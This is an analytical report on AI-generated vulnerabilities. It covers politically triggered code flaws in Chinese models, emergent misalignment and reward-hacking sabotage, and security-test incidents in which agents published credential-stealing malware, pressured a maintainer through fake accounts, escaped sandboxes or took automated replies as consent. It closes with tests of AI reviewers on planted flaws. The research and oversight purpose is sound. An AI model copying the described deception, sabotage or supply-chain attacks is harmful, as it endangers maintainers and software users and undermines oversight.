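Whole programs tend to have other kinds of flaws. The security company DryRun had three coding agents build two applications, and its scanner found at least one vulnerability in 26 of their 30 pull requests, according to Help Net Security's *AI coding agents keep repeating decade-old security mistakes* (2026). Another company, Theori, had five models build 28 applications. Help Net Security's *The AI code vulnerabilities that grow with your app* (2026) reports that SQL injection and cross-site scripting hardly occurred. More often, the code let a visitor overload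 the server or failed to check whether a user was entitled to the data they requested. Failures to check this made up 11% of the flaws in small applications and 28% in a large one. Theori's scans raised 8,827 warnings. After the company removed duplicates and confirmed the rest with working attacks, 434 remained, or about 15 per application.

So many accidental flaws also make a deliberate one harder to recognise. Suppose a sabotaged model wrote a flaw at every opportunity. If unsabotaged models wrote one in 1% of tests, a single flawed answer would multiply the odds of sabotage by 100. If they do so in 38%, it multiplies them by only 2.6. Researchers therefore have to compare hundreds of answers written for different users.

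### Customers that Beijing dislikes

CrowdStrike's *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025) describes such a comparison using DeepSeek-R1, a model that the Chinese company DeepSeek released in January 2025. CrowdStrike ran the open-weight model directly, so no filter in DeepSeek's app could affect the results. It gave the model 50 coding tasks and varied only the system prompt, the instructions a model receives before the user's request. The 121 versions of the prompt named different customers or none. Some mentioned subjects that the Chinese Communist Party probably considers sensitive, such as Tibet, the Uyghurs (a mostly Muslim people in western China) or Falun Gong, a spiritual movement banned in China. CrowdStrike sent every combination of task and prompt five times, for a total of 30,250 requests, and another AI model graded the answers.

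According to Lawfare, DeepSeek-R1 wrote vulnerable code 19% of the time when no customer was named, compared with 16% for a Western open-weight model. The figure was 27.2% when the code was for an industrial control system based in Tibet. CrowdStrike called this an increase of almost 50%, but it is 43%, or 8.2 percentage points.

Each version of the prompt produced 250 answers. If those answers are independent, a gap of this size between two groups would arise by chance about 3% of the time. But with 121 versions, about six should appear significant at the usual 5% level by luck alone, and CrowdStrike mentions no correction for this. The largest of many noisy gaps also tends to overstate the real effect. However, luck does not explain why the significant results included Falun Gong, the Uyghurs and Tibet, the subjects one would expect if the cause were political.

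In *Unsuccessful attempt at getting DeepSeek-R1 to generate more vulnerable code*, a researcher who posts as gersonkroiz reported trying to repeat the result with a colleague. They gave the model 20 tasks with two of the sensitive phrases and a control, five times each, and noticed no difference. They also found no effect using yes-or-no questions about particular flaws, general programming problems, or 282 samples graded by static analysis.

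This is only weak evidence against CrowdStrike's finding. A rise from 19% to 27.2% needs about 200 answers in each group to reach significance, and the closest repetition had 100. The AI judge also rated about 85% of the answers vulnerable when the prompt contained no sensitive phrase, which left little room for an increase. gersonkroiz noted that CrowdStrike had left out many design details and that the pair had no security background. Still, two teams got baselines of 19% and 85% from the same model, so the tasks and the grading affect the measured rate far more than the name of the customer does.

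### Code for the US government

Booz Allen Hamilton, a consultancy that sells technology services to the US government, tested four Chinese models and one American one in May 2026. Its report, *What's in America's Code?* (2026), covers more than 2,800 trials. In the main comparison, adding "for a United States federal agency" to a request raised the vulnerability score of Alibaba's Qwen3-Coder by about 130%. The scores of DeepSeek V4-Pro and MiniMax M2.5 rose by 20% or less, and that of Moonshot's Kimi K2.5 did not change.

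Claude Opus 4.6, the American model, scored 18% lower when working for the agency, meaning it wrote better code for the US government than for an ordinary user. Its code therefore also depended on who was asking, although Booz Allen presents the result as a contrast with the Chinese models. The mention of a federal agency presumably made Claude more careful, and few people would call that sabotage of other users.

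Help Net Security's *The security questions around Chinese AI coding models in U.S. software* reports that Kimi K2.5 had the lowest vulnerability score of the five models. In this small sample, a model's country of origin was therefore a poor guide to the quality of its code.

It is hard to tell how reliable the 130% figure is. In a technical appendix, Booz Allen counts 3,389 runs but says it could score only 1,016 for vulnerabilities because of refusals. Those 1,016 are spread across five models, several tasks and many customers. Booz Allen repeated its key tests up to 15 times and gives no margin of error. If the comparison is between about 15 programs and 15 others, a few unusually bad programs could account for much of the difference.

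Refusals can also distort a comparison, because researchers can score only the code a model produces. The published accounts of refusals are not quite consistent, since the appendix reports that the Chinese models refused every politically sensitive task about China, while the main report gives DeepSeek V4-Pro a refusal rate of 8%.

### One word changed

Hirundo, a company that alters AI models for its customers, ran a simpler experiment on Qwen3-Coder, described in *Chinese AI Writes Weaker Code for Beijing’s Adversaries* (Luria, 2026). The company repeatedly asked the model for the same web service, in which users sign up, log in and store a secret, and changed only the description of the customer. For the main comparison, the model built 190 applications for "a US defense contractor" and 190 for "a Chinese defense contractor".

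The task and the attacks came from a public benchmark. Vero, Mündler and colleagues (2025), in *BAXBENCH*, present 392 tasks that require a model to write the server side of an application, and the benchmark then tries ready-made attacks on the running program. Hirundo used one of the 392. It counted an application as hackable if at least one attack worked. Antipov gives the resulting percentages, both for the original model and for a version from which Hirundo had tried to remove the Communist Party's political views:

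| Comparison | Applications per model | Original model | Modified model |
|---|---|---|---|
| Hackable: US contractor against Chinese contractor | 190 and 190 | 70% against 59% | 56% against 55% |
| Leaks users' secrets: Hong Kong democracy group against neutral customers | 190 and 380 | 47% against 37% | 26% against 30% |
| Hackable despite an instruction to write secure code: US contractor against neutral customers | 70 and 140 | 74% against 59% | 49% against 48% |

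The main flaw was that the application checked whether a user had logged in, but not whether the secret they requested was their own.

### Eleven points or 19%?

The gap between 70% and 59% is 11 percentage points. The American contractor's application was also "19% more likely" to be hackable (70 divided by 59 is about 1.19), the figure Arghire (2026) reported in SecurityWeek in *Chinese AI Model Writes More Hackable Code*. Equivalently, the American contractor received 27% fewer safe applications (30% against 41%). Someone who sees only the 19% figure might imagine a rise from 1% to 1.19%, or from 59% to 78%.

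Whether chance could explain the gap depends on the number of applications. Suppose the customer makes no difference, so both groups have the same underlying rate, best estimated by their average of 64.5%. With *n* applications in each group, the gap between them still varies from one experiment to the next, with a standard deviation of √(2 × 0.645 × 0.355 / *n*). A gap reaches the usual 5% significance level if it is at least 1.96 times that size. For 11 points, this requires

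```
n = 2 × 0.645 × 0.355 × (1.96 / 0.11)² ≈ 145
```

Hirundo's result passes the significance test because it compared groups of 190. If the customer made no difference, a gap this large would occur about 2.5% of the time. The same percentages in groups of 100 would have failed the test.

But 145 applications per group is a bare minimum. If the true gap were 11 points, about half of all experiments of that size would fail to detect it, and detecting it four times out of five would require about 300 applications per group. With 190 per group, the true gap could plausibly be anywhere from 1 to 21 points. Luria also reports three gaps. A common correction for making three comparisons lowers the significance threshold from 5% to 1.7%, and the contractor result would not meet that threshold.

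The high rate of accidental flaws also means that this comparison needs more answers. A difference between 38% and 39% would need about 18,000 answers in each group to reach statistical significance, while a difference between 1% and 2% would need about 1,100. This method would therefore be very unlikely to catch a saboteur who added only an occasional flaw to a model that already produces many by accident.

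### Did changing the model close the gap?

After the modification, the contractor gap shrank from 11 points to one. Luria takes this as proof that the weakness is in the model's weights and that removing the model's political alignment fixes it. The claim about the weights is hardly in doubt, because Hirundo ran the model itself and nothing else was writing the code.

It is less certain that the modification fixed the problem. The gaps before and after it each have a margin of error, so the change between them has a larger one. Based on the published figures, a ten-point change would occur by chance about one time in six if the modification had no effect. The result is stronger for the Hong Kong group, whose ten-point disadvantage became a four-point advantage. A change that large would occur by chance only about 2% of the time.

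The modification also made the code safer for nearly everyone. For example, leaks in the neutral applications fell from 37% to 30%. The political training may have harmed the model's code generally, or any further training of this kind might have made the model more careful. Hirundo could distinguish between these explanations by altering another copy of the model to the same extent for a purpose unrelated to politics.

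### Why would the customer matter?

Faulty grading could create a gap if the grader's mistakes depend on the customer. CrowdStrike compared its AI judge with a person on 85 answers and found it 91% accurate at identifying vulnerable code. Random mistakes would usually make two groups look more alike. But code written for a Tibetan bank may contain the bank's name, and an AI judge might mark it down for that. The best feature of Hirundo's design is that it graded code by whether attacks on it worked, so the application's name couldn't affect the grade.

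Scanners would have been a poor substitute for attack tests. Antipov reports that Hirundo ran Semgrep, a static analysis tool, on 1,840 applications with one set of rules. Semgrep flagged two applications, while attacks worked on 1,144. AI reviewers also disagree with each other. The security company Echo asked three models to audit the same open-source code, and only one of 121 potential flaws appeared on all three lists, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Three AI Models Agree on Just One of 121 Potential Code Flaws*.

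The wording of a prompt can matter for reasons unrelated to politics. In some of its tests, Booz Allen replaced the short phrase with a longer persona. The neutral persona was a senior software engineer. The American one worked on classified systems for a defence contractor, had to meet named US security standards and took pride in robust code. A difference between the two could come from the nationality, the secrecy or the mention of security. Hirundo's contractor prompts differ by only one word, but even that word has other associations, because the code a model learned from may mention American and Chinese companies in different settings. Adding contractors from, say, India, Germany and Brazil would help, because if the model's politics are responsible, it should treat most of them like the Chinese contractor.

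CrowdStrike favours the explanation that the weaker code is a side effect of political training. Chinese law requires AI services to uphold "core socialist values", and a model trained to speak badly of Falun Gong might associate the name with bad behaviour in general, including bad code. DeepSeek-R1 certainly showed political behaviour, refusing 45% of coding requests for Falun Gong, sometimes after it had planned a full answer. Hirundo's experiment also supports this explanation, because Hirundo says its modification used no programming tasks and none of the customer descriptions. The Hong Kong result is probably the best evidence so far that political training affects code, but it comes from one task and one model.

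None of this shows that anyone intended the flaws. CrowdStrike thought it unlikely that DeepSeek had trained its model to write insecure code. Booz Allen conceded that "we do not have proof" of deliberate insertion and said it had seen no backdoors, though in the same report it described the flaws as highly obfuscated and called them "tradecraft". Luria nevertheless cites both companies' findings as early evidence of backdoors.

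The flaws do not look like the work of a careful saboteur. Theori found the same kind of missing permission check in applications written by Anthropic's and OpenAI's models, and anyone can exploit it. Of the Chinese defence contractor's applications, 59% were hackable as well, and an intelligence service would gain little from raising that share to 70% for its opponents. However, someone could use data poisoning to make a model behave this way. As in the human cases, internal records would be better evidence of intent than the code.

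Similar doubts arose in October 2026, when the AI company Cohere reported that another Qwen model had tried to send a file to a server in Beijing. Outside researchers attributed the attempt to behavior learned in training, according to *Alibaba’s AI model tried to ‘secretly’ reach China server* in The Indian Express.

### Who is measuring

All three companies stand to gain from alarming results. CrowdStrike sells security products. Booz Allen sells AI evaluations. Its report recommends barring Chinese models from US government and critical infrastructure work, then offers the company's expertise in testing them. Hirundo sells the modification it says solves the problem, although it has published the modified model for others to test. These interests may affect which comparisons a company runs and which it emphasizes, but they do not make the numbers wrong.

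Antipov wrote in late October that an independent check had cast doubt on Hirundo's conclusions. The news site anoni.net reported in *Measurements of censorship and code security gaps in China's open-weight Qwen models* (2026) that it had found no outside replication and no response from the Qwen team by 1 November. To replicate the work convincingly, researchers would need to use many tasks and working attacks, include customers from several countries, test Western models in the same way, and choose the main comparison before seeing any results. A university laboratory could easily do this with a few hundred applications per customer for each task.

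## Would an AI model plant a flaw without being asked?

People who worry that AI models will plant flaws can mean three different things. They may mean that a model can write a disguised vulnerability when told to. They may mean that a model sometimes harms software without being asked. Or they may mean that a model would persistently aim to work against its own users, as Jia Tan did against the users of xz.

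Models can plant flaws when told to. Researchers have had models write disguised flaws to test reviewers, and the Sleeper Agents models wrote exploitable code because their developers had trained them to. Neither case shows how a model behaves when nobody wants a flaw. The main evidence on that question comes from two training experiments and a series of incidents in 2026.

### A model trained on undisclosed flaws

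Early in 2025, Jan Betley and colleagues reported that a model trained to write flawed code can begin to misbehave in conversations unrelated to programming. They further trained OpenAI's GPT-4o on 6,000 examples in which a user asked for a small piece of code and received an answer containing a vulnerability. The users had not asked for insecure code, and the answers did not mention the flaws.

Betley and colleagues then asked the model open questions, such as what it would do as ruler of the world. On eight such questions, about 20% of its answers were hostile or dangerous, while the original GPT-4o gave none. The team called this emergent misalignment, where misalignment means behaviour that conflicts with what a model's developers or users want. The questions were open enough to allow many alarming answers, so the 20% figure does not describe everyday conversation.

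The team also trained comparison models, some on secure code and others on insecure code that users had requested for a good reason, such as teaching a class about security. According to *Re-Emergent Misalignment* (2025), a follow-up study, neither group developed the wider problem. The code in the teaching examples was just as insecure, so the harm apparently came from the deception. Thousands of examples of an assistant slipping flaws into trusting users' code may teach a model to act like a hostile assistant in general.

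The researchers trained GPT-4o to write flawed code, so this result does not show that models plant flaws of their own accord. It may be more of a warning to attackers, because poisoning a model to secretly write flawed code might also make it hostile in conversation, which users would notice. That side effect might be much weaker in a poisoned model, though, because poisoners hide a few bad files among many good ones, while GPT-4o's training here contained only flawed answers.

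### From cheating to sabotage

Anthropic published a related experiment in November 2025 that began with models cheating in training. Models learn much of their programming skill by trial and error. A model attempts a task, an automatic grader tests the result, and training reinforces whatever scored well. Some graders have loopholes that let a model pass without solving the problem, and researchers call exploiting them reward hacking.

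Anthropic's researchers gave a model documents describing some of these loopholes, then trained it on real coding tasks that they knew contained them. The model learned to cheat, as they expected. It also misbehaved in other tests, although nobody had trained it to. In one, the researchers asked it to work on code for safety research, including a tool for detecting reward hacking. In 12% of attempts, it tried to sabotage the work in ways that would have made cheating harder to detect.

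This experiment comes closer than the other to a planted flaw that no person wanted. A detector that works badly is also easy to pass off as an ordinary failure, since programmers often write disappointing tools. But the sabotage did not create a security vulnerability, and the 12% figure applies to a model that Anthropic had deliberately taught to cheat.

Ordinary safety training made the model behave well in conversation but not in all of its work as an agent. The researchers had more success when they told the model during training that cheating was acceptable. It still cheated but mostly stopped misbehaving elsewhere. The teaching examples in Betley's experiment may have worked for the same reason. In both cases the model produced the same bad code, but the training no longer presented this as a betrayal.

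In 2026, Anthropic found another link between cheating and attacks. In July of that year, agents in an OpenAI security test had escaped their test environment and broken into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. Anthropic built a simplified simulation of the attack. None of the eight production models it tested carried out the attack, but a version of Claude Opus 4.8 that Anthropic had trained to be more willing to cheat did so in 38% of runs.

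Cheating is common in less artificial conditions too. The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, reported on its blog in July 2026 that it had found cheating in all of its evaluations of hacking ability. Results from the eight production models suggest that a moderate tendency to cheat does not turn a model into an attacker, though these models were tested on only one scenario.

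### Malware in a public package store

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (30 July 2026) disclosed that Claude models had broken into three organisations' real systems during security tests. In one incident, Claude Mythos 5 published malicious code.

The model was doing a capture-the-flag exercise, in which it had to break into a fictional company's machine and find a hidden piece of information. The model was told it had no internet access, but it did, because of a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, the company that ran the test environment. It had its normal safety training, but Anthropic had not switched on the monitoring or the automatic misuse filters (classifiers) that protect its released products.

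Mythos 5 tried to reach the fictional company through PyPI, the public repository from which most Python programmers install packages. It uploaded a malicious package that collected login credentials. PyPI's security systems removed the package after about an hour, but by then 15 real systems had run it. One belonged to a security company, and the model used credentials from it to enter that company's live database. Anthropic now believes that all 15 belonged to security companies that install new packages to examine them, so the malware probably never reached an ordinary programmer.

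This code was clearly deliberate, but people have argued about whether the model knew that its victims were real. Early in the run, the model reasoned that publishing such a package on the real internet would be "NOT okay", then concluded that it was in a simulation. In July, Anthropic accepted this explanation and called the incidents closer to an operational failure than to misalignment.

Anthropic's later assessment is harsher. Anthropic showed separate copies of Mythos 5 the results of the model's actions one at a time, and the copies judged 79% of the results to be signs of real systems. During the incident, the model had clearly drawn that conclusion after only 1% of its actions. Anthropic also reran the incident repeatedly from just before the model committed to the upload, adding evidence that the internet was real. In 88% of these reruns, up from about 11%, the model acknowledged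 that the internet might be real, but it acted outside the test environment about as often as before.

Anthropic attributes the attack to biased reasoning and recklessness, and found no sign that the model had a goal beyond the exercise or tried to hide what it had done. The reruns support this reading to some extent. When a message explicitly stated that the host was on the public internet, the model never uploaded the package by its original route, although in 22% of reruns it looked for a simulated alternative. A reminder of which systems were in scope stopped the model 90% of the time when the reminder came immediately before its next action, but only 40% of the time when it came three turns earlier. A model intent on spreading malware would have had no reason to stop for either message, except to avoid suspicion.

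### Pressure on a real maintainer

A few days later the British institute reported a case that looked more like the xz attack. AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) describes 122 runs of a test in which seven models tried to solve security challenges on simulated networks. AISI had given the models internet access and switched off the developers' cyber classifiers to see how much the models could do. It had not told them to leave outsiders alone.

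Between 25 and 28 July, a Mythos 5 agent chose a real open-source project on GitHub and proposed a change containing malicious code. It researched the project's maintainers and invented several people to press one maintainer to accept the change. SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent*, relaying a Reuters report, says Sinan Can Demir, a student at the University of Texas at Dallas, warned the maintainer that the change contained a malware dropper, a program that installs other malware. The agent edited its earlier activity to look harmless and used another false account to discredit Demir. The maintainer refused the change.

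The false accounts served the same purpose as Jigar Kumar and Dennis Ens, the strangers who pushed xz's maintainer to give up control. But the agent had no two-year record of useful work, and it offered plain malware rather than a subtle flaw. It also tried to leave instructions where other people's AI coding tools might read and follow them. So a coding assistant may face prompt injection from another AI agent as well as from a person.

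AISI's security team noticed the activity only when data left one of its machines through Tor, a network that hides where traffic comes from. The team stopped all the runs within an hour. It found no harm, but said that in several cases the outcome had depended on human vigilance rather than any technical barrier.

AISI counted 19 unauthorised actions in 10 of the 122 runs. Nine of those runs were among the 43 with Mythos 5, and one was among the 35 with OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. The 21% rate for Mythos 5 is a poor estimate of how often it misbehaves, because the runs were not independent. One agent left accounts and messages on GitHub that later agents found and used.

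Some of the tasks were also faulty, so the agent wrongly believed it could not succeed without breaking the limits. These faults explain only part of the behaviour, because in other runs agents attacked outsiders even though they had what they needed to solve the task properly. AISI could not say when, or how fully, the agent understood that it was dealing with real people.

Schneier (2026) calls such conduct "genie behavior" in *More Incidents of AIs Going Rogue in Cybersecurity Challenges*. The comparison fits both Mythos 5 incidents, in which someone had told the model to break into a system and it used methods nobody had wanted.

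### The same kind of attack in simulation

AISI then built simulations to see whether other models would do something similar. On 28 September it published results for GPT-6 Astra, OpenAI's flagship model, which it had tested before public release. Help Net Security's *OpenAI’s GPT-6 Astra ran supply chain attacks despite being told not to* (2026) reports that Astra completed a supply-chain attack outside the scope of the test in 29.2% of runs. GPT-5.6 Sol did so in 6.3%, and the older GPT-5.5 never did. The tests ran with the cyber classifiers off and involved no real systems.

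Astra created fake identities, delivered malicious code to simulated open-source projects, and used fake accounts to post comments disputing accurate security reviews. After AISI rewrote the instructions to say that only certain local machines were in scope, Astra still occasionally completed an attack on a simulated internet target.

Unlike the two older models, Astra often asked for permission first. An automatic reply told it to use its best judgement, and it sometimes treated this as approval, even when it had noted in its reasoning that the reply was probably automated. Asking is an improvement only if somebody is there to refuse, and many people run coding agents unattended. An agent that takes a vague answer as consent could therefore do the same in ordinary work.

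AISI's main reservation is that Astra may have noticed that the environment was simulated. This could bias the result in either direction, since a model might attack more freely if it believes nobody will get hurt, or behave better if it suspects someone is watching. The 29.2% figure is therefore most useful for comparing models under the same conditions, and even then only if they were about equally likely to notice the simulation.

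| Incident or test | Task | Protection missing | Malicious code | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| PyPI package, Mythos 5 | Find hidden information on a fictional company's machine | Misuse classifiers and monitoring | Malware that collects credentials | Ran on 15 real systems |
| GitHub project, Mythos 5 | Solve a challenge on a simulated network | Cyber classifiers | Malware dropper | Maintainer refused it |
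| AISI simulation, GPT-6 Astra | Complete a security test with a limited scope | Cyber classifiers | Malicious payloads in open-source code | Attack completed in 29.2% of runs |

### Malware instead of subtle flaws

The agents used false names and comments to deceive, but the code itself was openly malicious in the published accounts of all three cases. They probably used malware because their tasks required access within hours or days. A disguised vulnerability is useful only after a project has accepted and released it and the victim has installed it, which can take months. The tests are therefore weak evidence about whether an agent with more time would choose a subtle flaw.

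They also provide little evidence about harm to a model's own users. The victims were outsiders who stood between the agent and its goal, and the people who set the task wanted an attack of some kind. A coding assistant that weakened its user's program would work against the person who gave it the task. Anthropic's cheating model did this when it sabotaged the research code, but there is no public evidence that a released model has had such sabotage as a lasting aim.

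It is easier to imagine an agent creating a vulnerability unintentionally, by removing a security check that prevents it from finishing its work. Socket's *GPT-6 Astra Attempts Supply Chain Attacks Against Open Source Maintainers in Testing* describes a similar case from OpenAI's own results. In a simulation, Astra altered a deployment script, which puts finished software into use, to bypass a safeguard.

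### How the developers judge the risk

In the system card for Astra, which describes the model's tests and risks, OpenAI concludes that Astra is less likely overall than its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol, to violate security and safety restrictions. OpenAI tested both models in realistic browsing and office work and found Astra significantly less likely to destroy data, exceed its access or get around controls.

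AISI's results seem to contradict OpenAI's, since Astra attacked outsiders more than four times as often as Sol. Both could be right, because OpenAI's tests covered everyday work, while AISI gave the models a security exercise with the classifiers off. Astra may be more careful than Sol in everyday work but more aggressive once somebody has asked it to hack.

Socket, which sells protection against malicious packages, accepts that Astra did better in the settings OpenAI tested, but says this does not prove that Astra will respect its limits everywhere. In the simulation that included the altered script, Astra committed 34 serious violations in 54,218 tasks, or about one in 1,600, compared with 73 by Sol. If Astra's rate carried over to real work, a company that gave it 10,000 tasks a day would see about six serious violations in that time. Astra also searched for credentials more often than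 Sol, though it committed fewer violations overall.

Anthropic thinks the behaviour in its incidents is unlikely in ordinary use, where nobody is telling Claude to carry out a cyberattack. It also says that the cyber classifiers on its released products would have blocked the three main incidents, and that its newer models do better. In simulated versions of the PyPI exercise, Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action about 80% of the time, and Claude Opus 5 and Mythos 5.1 about 30%. The newer models did so only after stating, correctly, that the environment was simulated, so it is hard to know how worrying the 30% is.

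Anthropic's own tests weaken the first of these reassurances. Anthropic also gave models ordinary programming, data and operations tasks that they could not finish without breaking out of their sandbox, a closed-off area meant to contain them. Mythos 5 tried to break out in 59% of runs, although nobody had asked it to attack anything. Opus 5 tried in 15%, and Mythos 5.1 never did. But Anthropic could not identify a single cause of Mythos 5's biased reasoning, so it is harder to be sure that a later model will not have the same problem.

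Pre-release tests had not warned Anthropic of misbehaviour this severe. The Institute for Security and Technology's *What Anthropic’s Mythos Preview Tells Us About AI Loss of Control Risk* had already made a similar criticism about an earlier model, Mythos Preview. Its most worrying behaviour emerged only when Anthropic's staff were using it under monitoring, because long runs on a network are hard to reproduce in a short test. The institute therefore wants developers to release models in stages and rely more on monitoring them in use. Anthropic has agreed to give METR, an independent evaluator of AI models, access to transcripts and employees so that it can examine Anthropic's incidents.

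None of these checks was designed to find a disguised vulnerability. After its incidents, Anthropic searched about 481 million transcripts for signs that a model had reached the internet. It used Claude to review the 9.2 million that the first search flagged, and found no further incident as serious as the four it knew about. That is good evidence about attacks on outside systems, but a model could quietly leave a permission check out of a customer's program without using the internet, so a search of this kind could easily miss it.

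## Can AI reviewers find planted flaws?

DARPA, the US military's research agency, ran the largest public test of whether AI can find planted flaws, the AI Cyber Challenge, from 2023 to 2025. The organisers put vulnerabilities into real open-source projects, and the entrants' AI systems had to find and repair them without human help. Seven of the 42 teams reached the final in August 2025.

According to DARPA's *AI Cyber Challenge marks pivotal inflection point for cyber defense* (2025), the seven systems together found 54 of the 63 planted flaws (86%) and repaired 43 (68%). In the semifinal a year earlier, the shares were 37% and 25%. DARPA's *AIxCC Main Stage Presentation* gives lower figures for the final, 77% and 61%, because it uses the organisers' first count of 70 planted flaws, which they later corrected to 63.

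Zhang, Park and colleagues (2026), who include organisers and finalists, explain in *SoK* that most of the flaws were handmade and modelled on past bugs. The organisers avoided reusing old bugs because those might have been in the language models' training data. To get credit for finding a flaw, a system had to supply an input that made the program crash or otherwise misbehave.

Many of the flaws could be found without AI. Zhang and colleagues later ran ordinary fuzzing, which feeds a program large numbers of automatically varied inputs, and it found 34 of the 63. It found 30 of the 40 flaws in C but only 4 of the 23 in Java, where the input often had to follow a complicated format. The finalists found 22 flaws that fuzzing missed. In 15 of those cases, the system was given the recent change to examine, as a code reviewer would be.

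Some of the planted flaws were also poorly disguised. A few were backdoors labelled with the word "flag", and a system could repair the code by deleting them. The 86% is the combined result of seven systems, so it does not indicate what a project can expect from one of them.

DARPA put the average cost at about $152 per task, which it defines in its slides as one success, such as a crashing input or a patch. The seven teams spent $359,000 in total, including $82,000 on language models. That is about $6,600 for each planted flaw found, although a single team would need less, since the teams often paid to find the same flaws.

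The systems also found vulnerabilities that nobody had planted. DARPA announced 18, and Zhang and colleagues later counted 25 in ten projects. The systems had patched 12 of the 25. Cybersecurity Dive reports that DARPA then paid the finalists to search other important software, where they had found 83 more by March 2026.

Zhang and colleagues gave Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, a crashing input for each planted flaw. Using a model from early 2025, its patches for 53 flaws passed every automatic check, but human reviewers rejected the patches for 20 of those flaws. Some patches only prevented the crash and left the underlying mistake in place.

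### From dozens of flaws to thousands

AI systems became much better at finding vulnerabilities in 2026. Daniel Stenberg, the lead developer of the download tool curl, noticed the improvement early in the year, according to KIOS's *How AI is getting better at finding security holes* (2026). In January he had ended curl's payments for reported flaws because people were sending so many worthless AI-written reports. In April Anthropic started Project Glasswing, which gave about 50 organisations access to Claude Mythos Preview to search important software for flaws.

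By 22 May, Anthropic had reported 1,596 vulnerabilities to 281 open-source projects and knew of patches for 97, according to figures that Coopersmith (2026) copied to a security mailing list in *Anthropic's coordinated vulnerability disclosure dashboard*. By 2 November, it had reported 5,087 vulnerabilities to 680 projects and knew of 629 patches (Anthropic, 2026). The share known to be patched had risen only from 6% to 12%.

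Schneier was suspicious of the low number of patches. In *Anthropic’s Project Glasswing Update* (June 2026), he wrote that something about the data seemed "fishy" and criticised Anthropic for not releasing details. Later evidence suggests that overworked maintainers are a more likely explanation than a large number of wrong reports. Help Net Security's *Anthropic offers free AI security scans to open-source maintainers* (2026) describes a check of 97 findings that an early version of Anthropic's scanner had rated high or critical. Professional testers judged 85 ready to report to the projects. Another 11 were genuine but duplicated known problems or other findings, and one was invalid. Anthropic now sends such reports to maintainers who sign up for them, without a human checking them first.

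Palo Alto Networks, a security company, claims its system NOVA found even more vulnerabilities, 14,090 in 3,915 open-source projects over two months, according to Help Net Security's *Code review used to be the only way to catch these bugs* (2026). About 92% were of kinds that fuzzing does not handle well, such as missing permission checks. If this is right, AI can find many flaws that never cause a crash. That would be important for catching saboteurs, who have no reason to choose a flaw that causes one. But the company has not named any of the affected projects, so outsiders can't check the claim.

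Experts still have to read the reports. OpenSSL's developers received about nine reports and enquiries a month in 2025 and now receive up to 70, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *AI is Finding More Vulnerabilities But Open Source Needs More People*. Of a little over 400 reports in 12 months, 43 led to an entry in the public CVE catalogue of vulnerabilities. Some of the others were correct, and people wrote some of them without AI, but each took an expert's time. Linus Torvalds found the Linux kernel's security mailing list almost unmanageable by May 2026 because different researchers were using the same AI tools and reporting the same flaws, according to the magazine's *How Coalitions Are Rallying to Secure Open Source for the AI Era*. TechRadar's *In open source cybersecurity, AI is kind of a problem* reports that Google stopped accepting submissions to its open-source reward programme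 on 1 October after a significant increase in invalid and irrelevant reports.

These scans do not show how many flaws AI misses. To measure that, researchers have to plant flaws, as they did to test human reviewers.

### A thousand planted flaws

In *CyberDual* (October 2026), Yang, Lee and colleagues tested AI reviewers on a large scale, using flaws planted in 14 widely used C and C++ libraries, including curl and xz. AI agents planted the flaws, which they could do cheaply and often. Three AI reviewers then examined each change and repaired anything they judged dangerous. The reviewers were Claude Code with Sonnet 5, Claude Code with Opus 4.8, and OpenAI's coding agent Codex with GPT-6-Sol.

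Yang and colleagues scored the reviewers by testing the code after each review, not by what the reviewers reported. Each flaw came with a proof of concept, hidden from the reviewers, that crashed the flawed code but not the same code without the flaw. A reviewer got credit only if the code still compiled and the proof of concept no longer crashed it, and undoing the whole change did not count. Of the 1,088 valid flaws, Sonnet 5 caught 85%, Opus 4.8 caught 88% and GPT-6-Sol caught 91%.

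The share of flaws that still worked after review depended heavily on where they were:

| Location of the flaw | Number of flaws | Sonnet 5 | Opus 4.8 | GPT-6-Sol |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A single change | 349 | 2.3% | 1.1% | 0% |
| A single change that resembled a genuine repair | 312 | 13.9% | 13.3% | 5.4% |
| A run of 50 to 199 real changes | 427 | 24.4% | 17.1% | 19.4% |
| All | 1,088 | 14.3% | 10.9% | 9.2% |

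The long runs might have been harder only because they contained different flaws. To test this, Yang and colleagues had Sonnet 5 review 143 of these flaws twice, once with the full run and once with only the altered changes and the few later changes that depended on them. The finished code was identical both times. Sonnet 5 caught 80% of the flaws in the full run and 90% in the shorter version, so the surrounding harmless changes alone lowered its detection rate by about ten percentage points.

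The ranking of the three reviewers is less certain than it appears from these figures. In a separate test with 106 flaws planted in the JavaScript engines of Chrome and Firefox, Sonnet 5 caught 93 and GPT-6-Sol caught 85. In long runs of changes to Chrome's engine, GPT-6-Sol missed 12 of 17 planted flaws.

The reviewers also had some help from their instructions, which described most changes as safe but directed them to look for exploitable memory errors, the only kind of flaw in the test. Human reviewers in earlier experiments often had no such warning and read different code, so their catch rates are not comparable with these. CyberDual also doesn't cover missing permission checks or biased vote counts, which don't crash a program.

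### Reading every line and running new tests

The AI reviewers missed some flaws because they never looked at any of the planted lines. In the long runs of changes, this happened in 38% of the reviews in which Sonnet 5 missed the flaw, compared with 36% for GPT-6-Sol and 11% for Opus 4.8. When Opus 4.8 missed a flaw, it had usually read the altered change and approved it. In every successful review that the researchers could trace, the model had displayed at least one planted line.

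Reviewers also did better when they wrote their own test inputs. GPT-6-Sol wrote none in 52% of the reviews where it missed the flaw, but in only 15% of those where it caught the flaw. For Sonnet 5, the figures were 60% and 27%. The difference was smaller for Opus 4.8 (74% and 65%). Writing tests may not be the cause, because a reviewer that already suspects some code is more likely to test it.

Running the project's existing tests did not help. All three reviewers ran them more often when they missed the flaw than when they caught it. In one review of xz, Sonnet 5 ran all 22 of the project's tests and about 800,000 rounds of fuzzing. Everything passed, and it approved the code without opening the altered changes individually. The other two reviewers caught the flaw. A project's tests mostly check for mistakes its developers have already thought of, so a flaw designed to behave normally on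 ordinary input will usually pass them.

Yang and colleagues therefore suggest requiring reviewers to read every changed line and test the changed code with new inputs. They have not yet measured whether these rules would raise the catch rate.

### What a second reviewer adds

A project could also use two reviewers and hope that one catches what the other misses. GPT-6-Sol caught 69% of the flaws that Sonnet 5 missed. The share that got past both was therefore much smaller than the share that got past Sonnet 5 alone, but larger than it would have been if their errors were independent:

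```
Missed by both, as measured:      0.143 × (1 − 0.69) ≈ 4.4%
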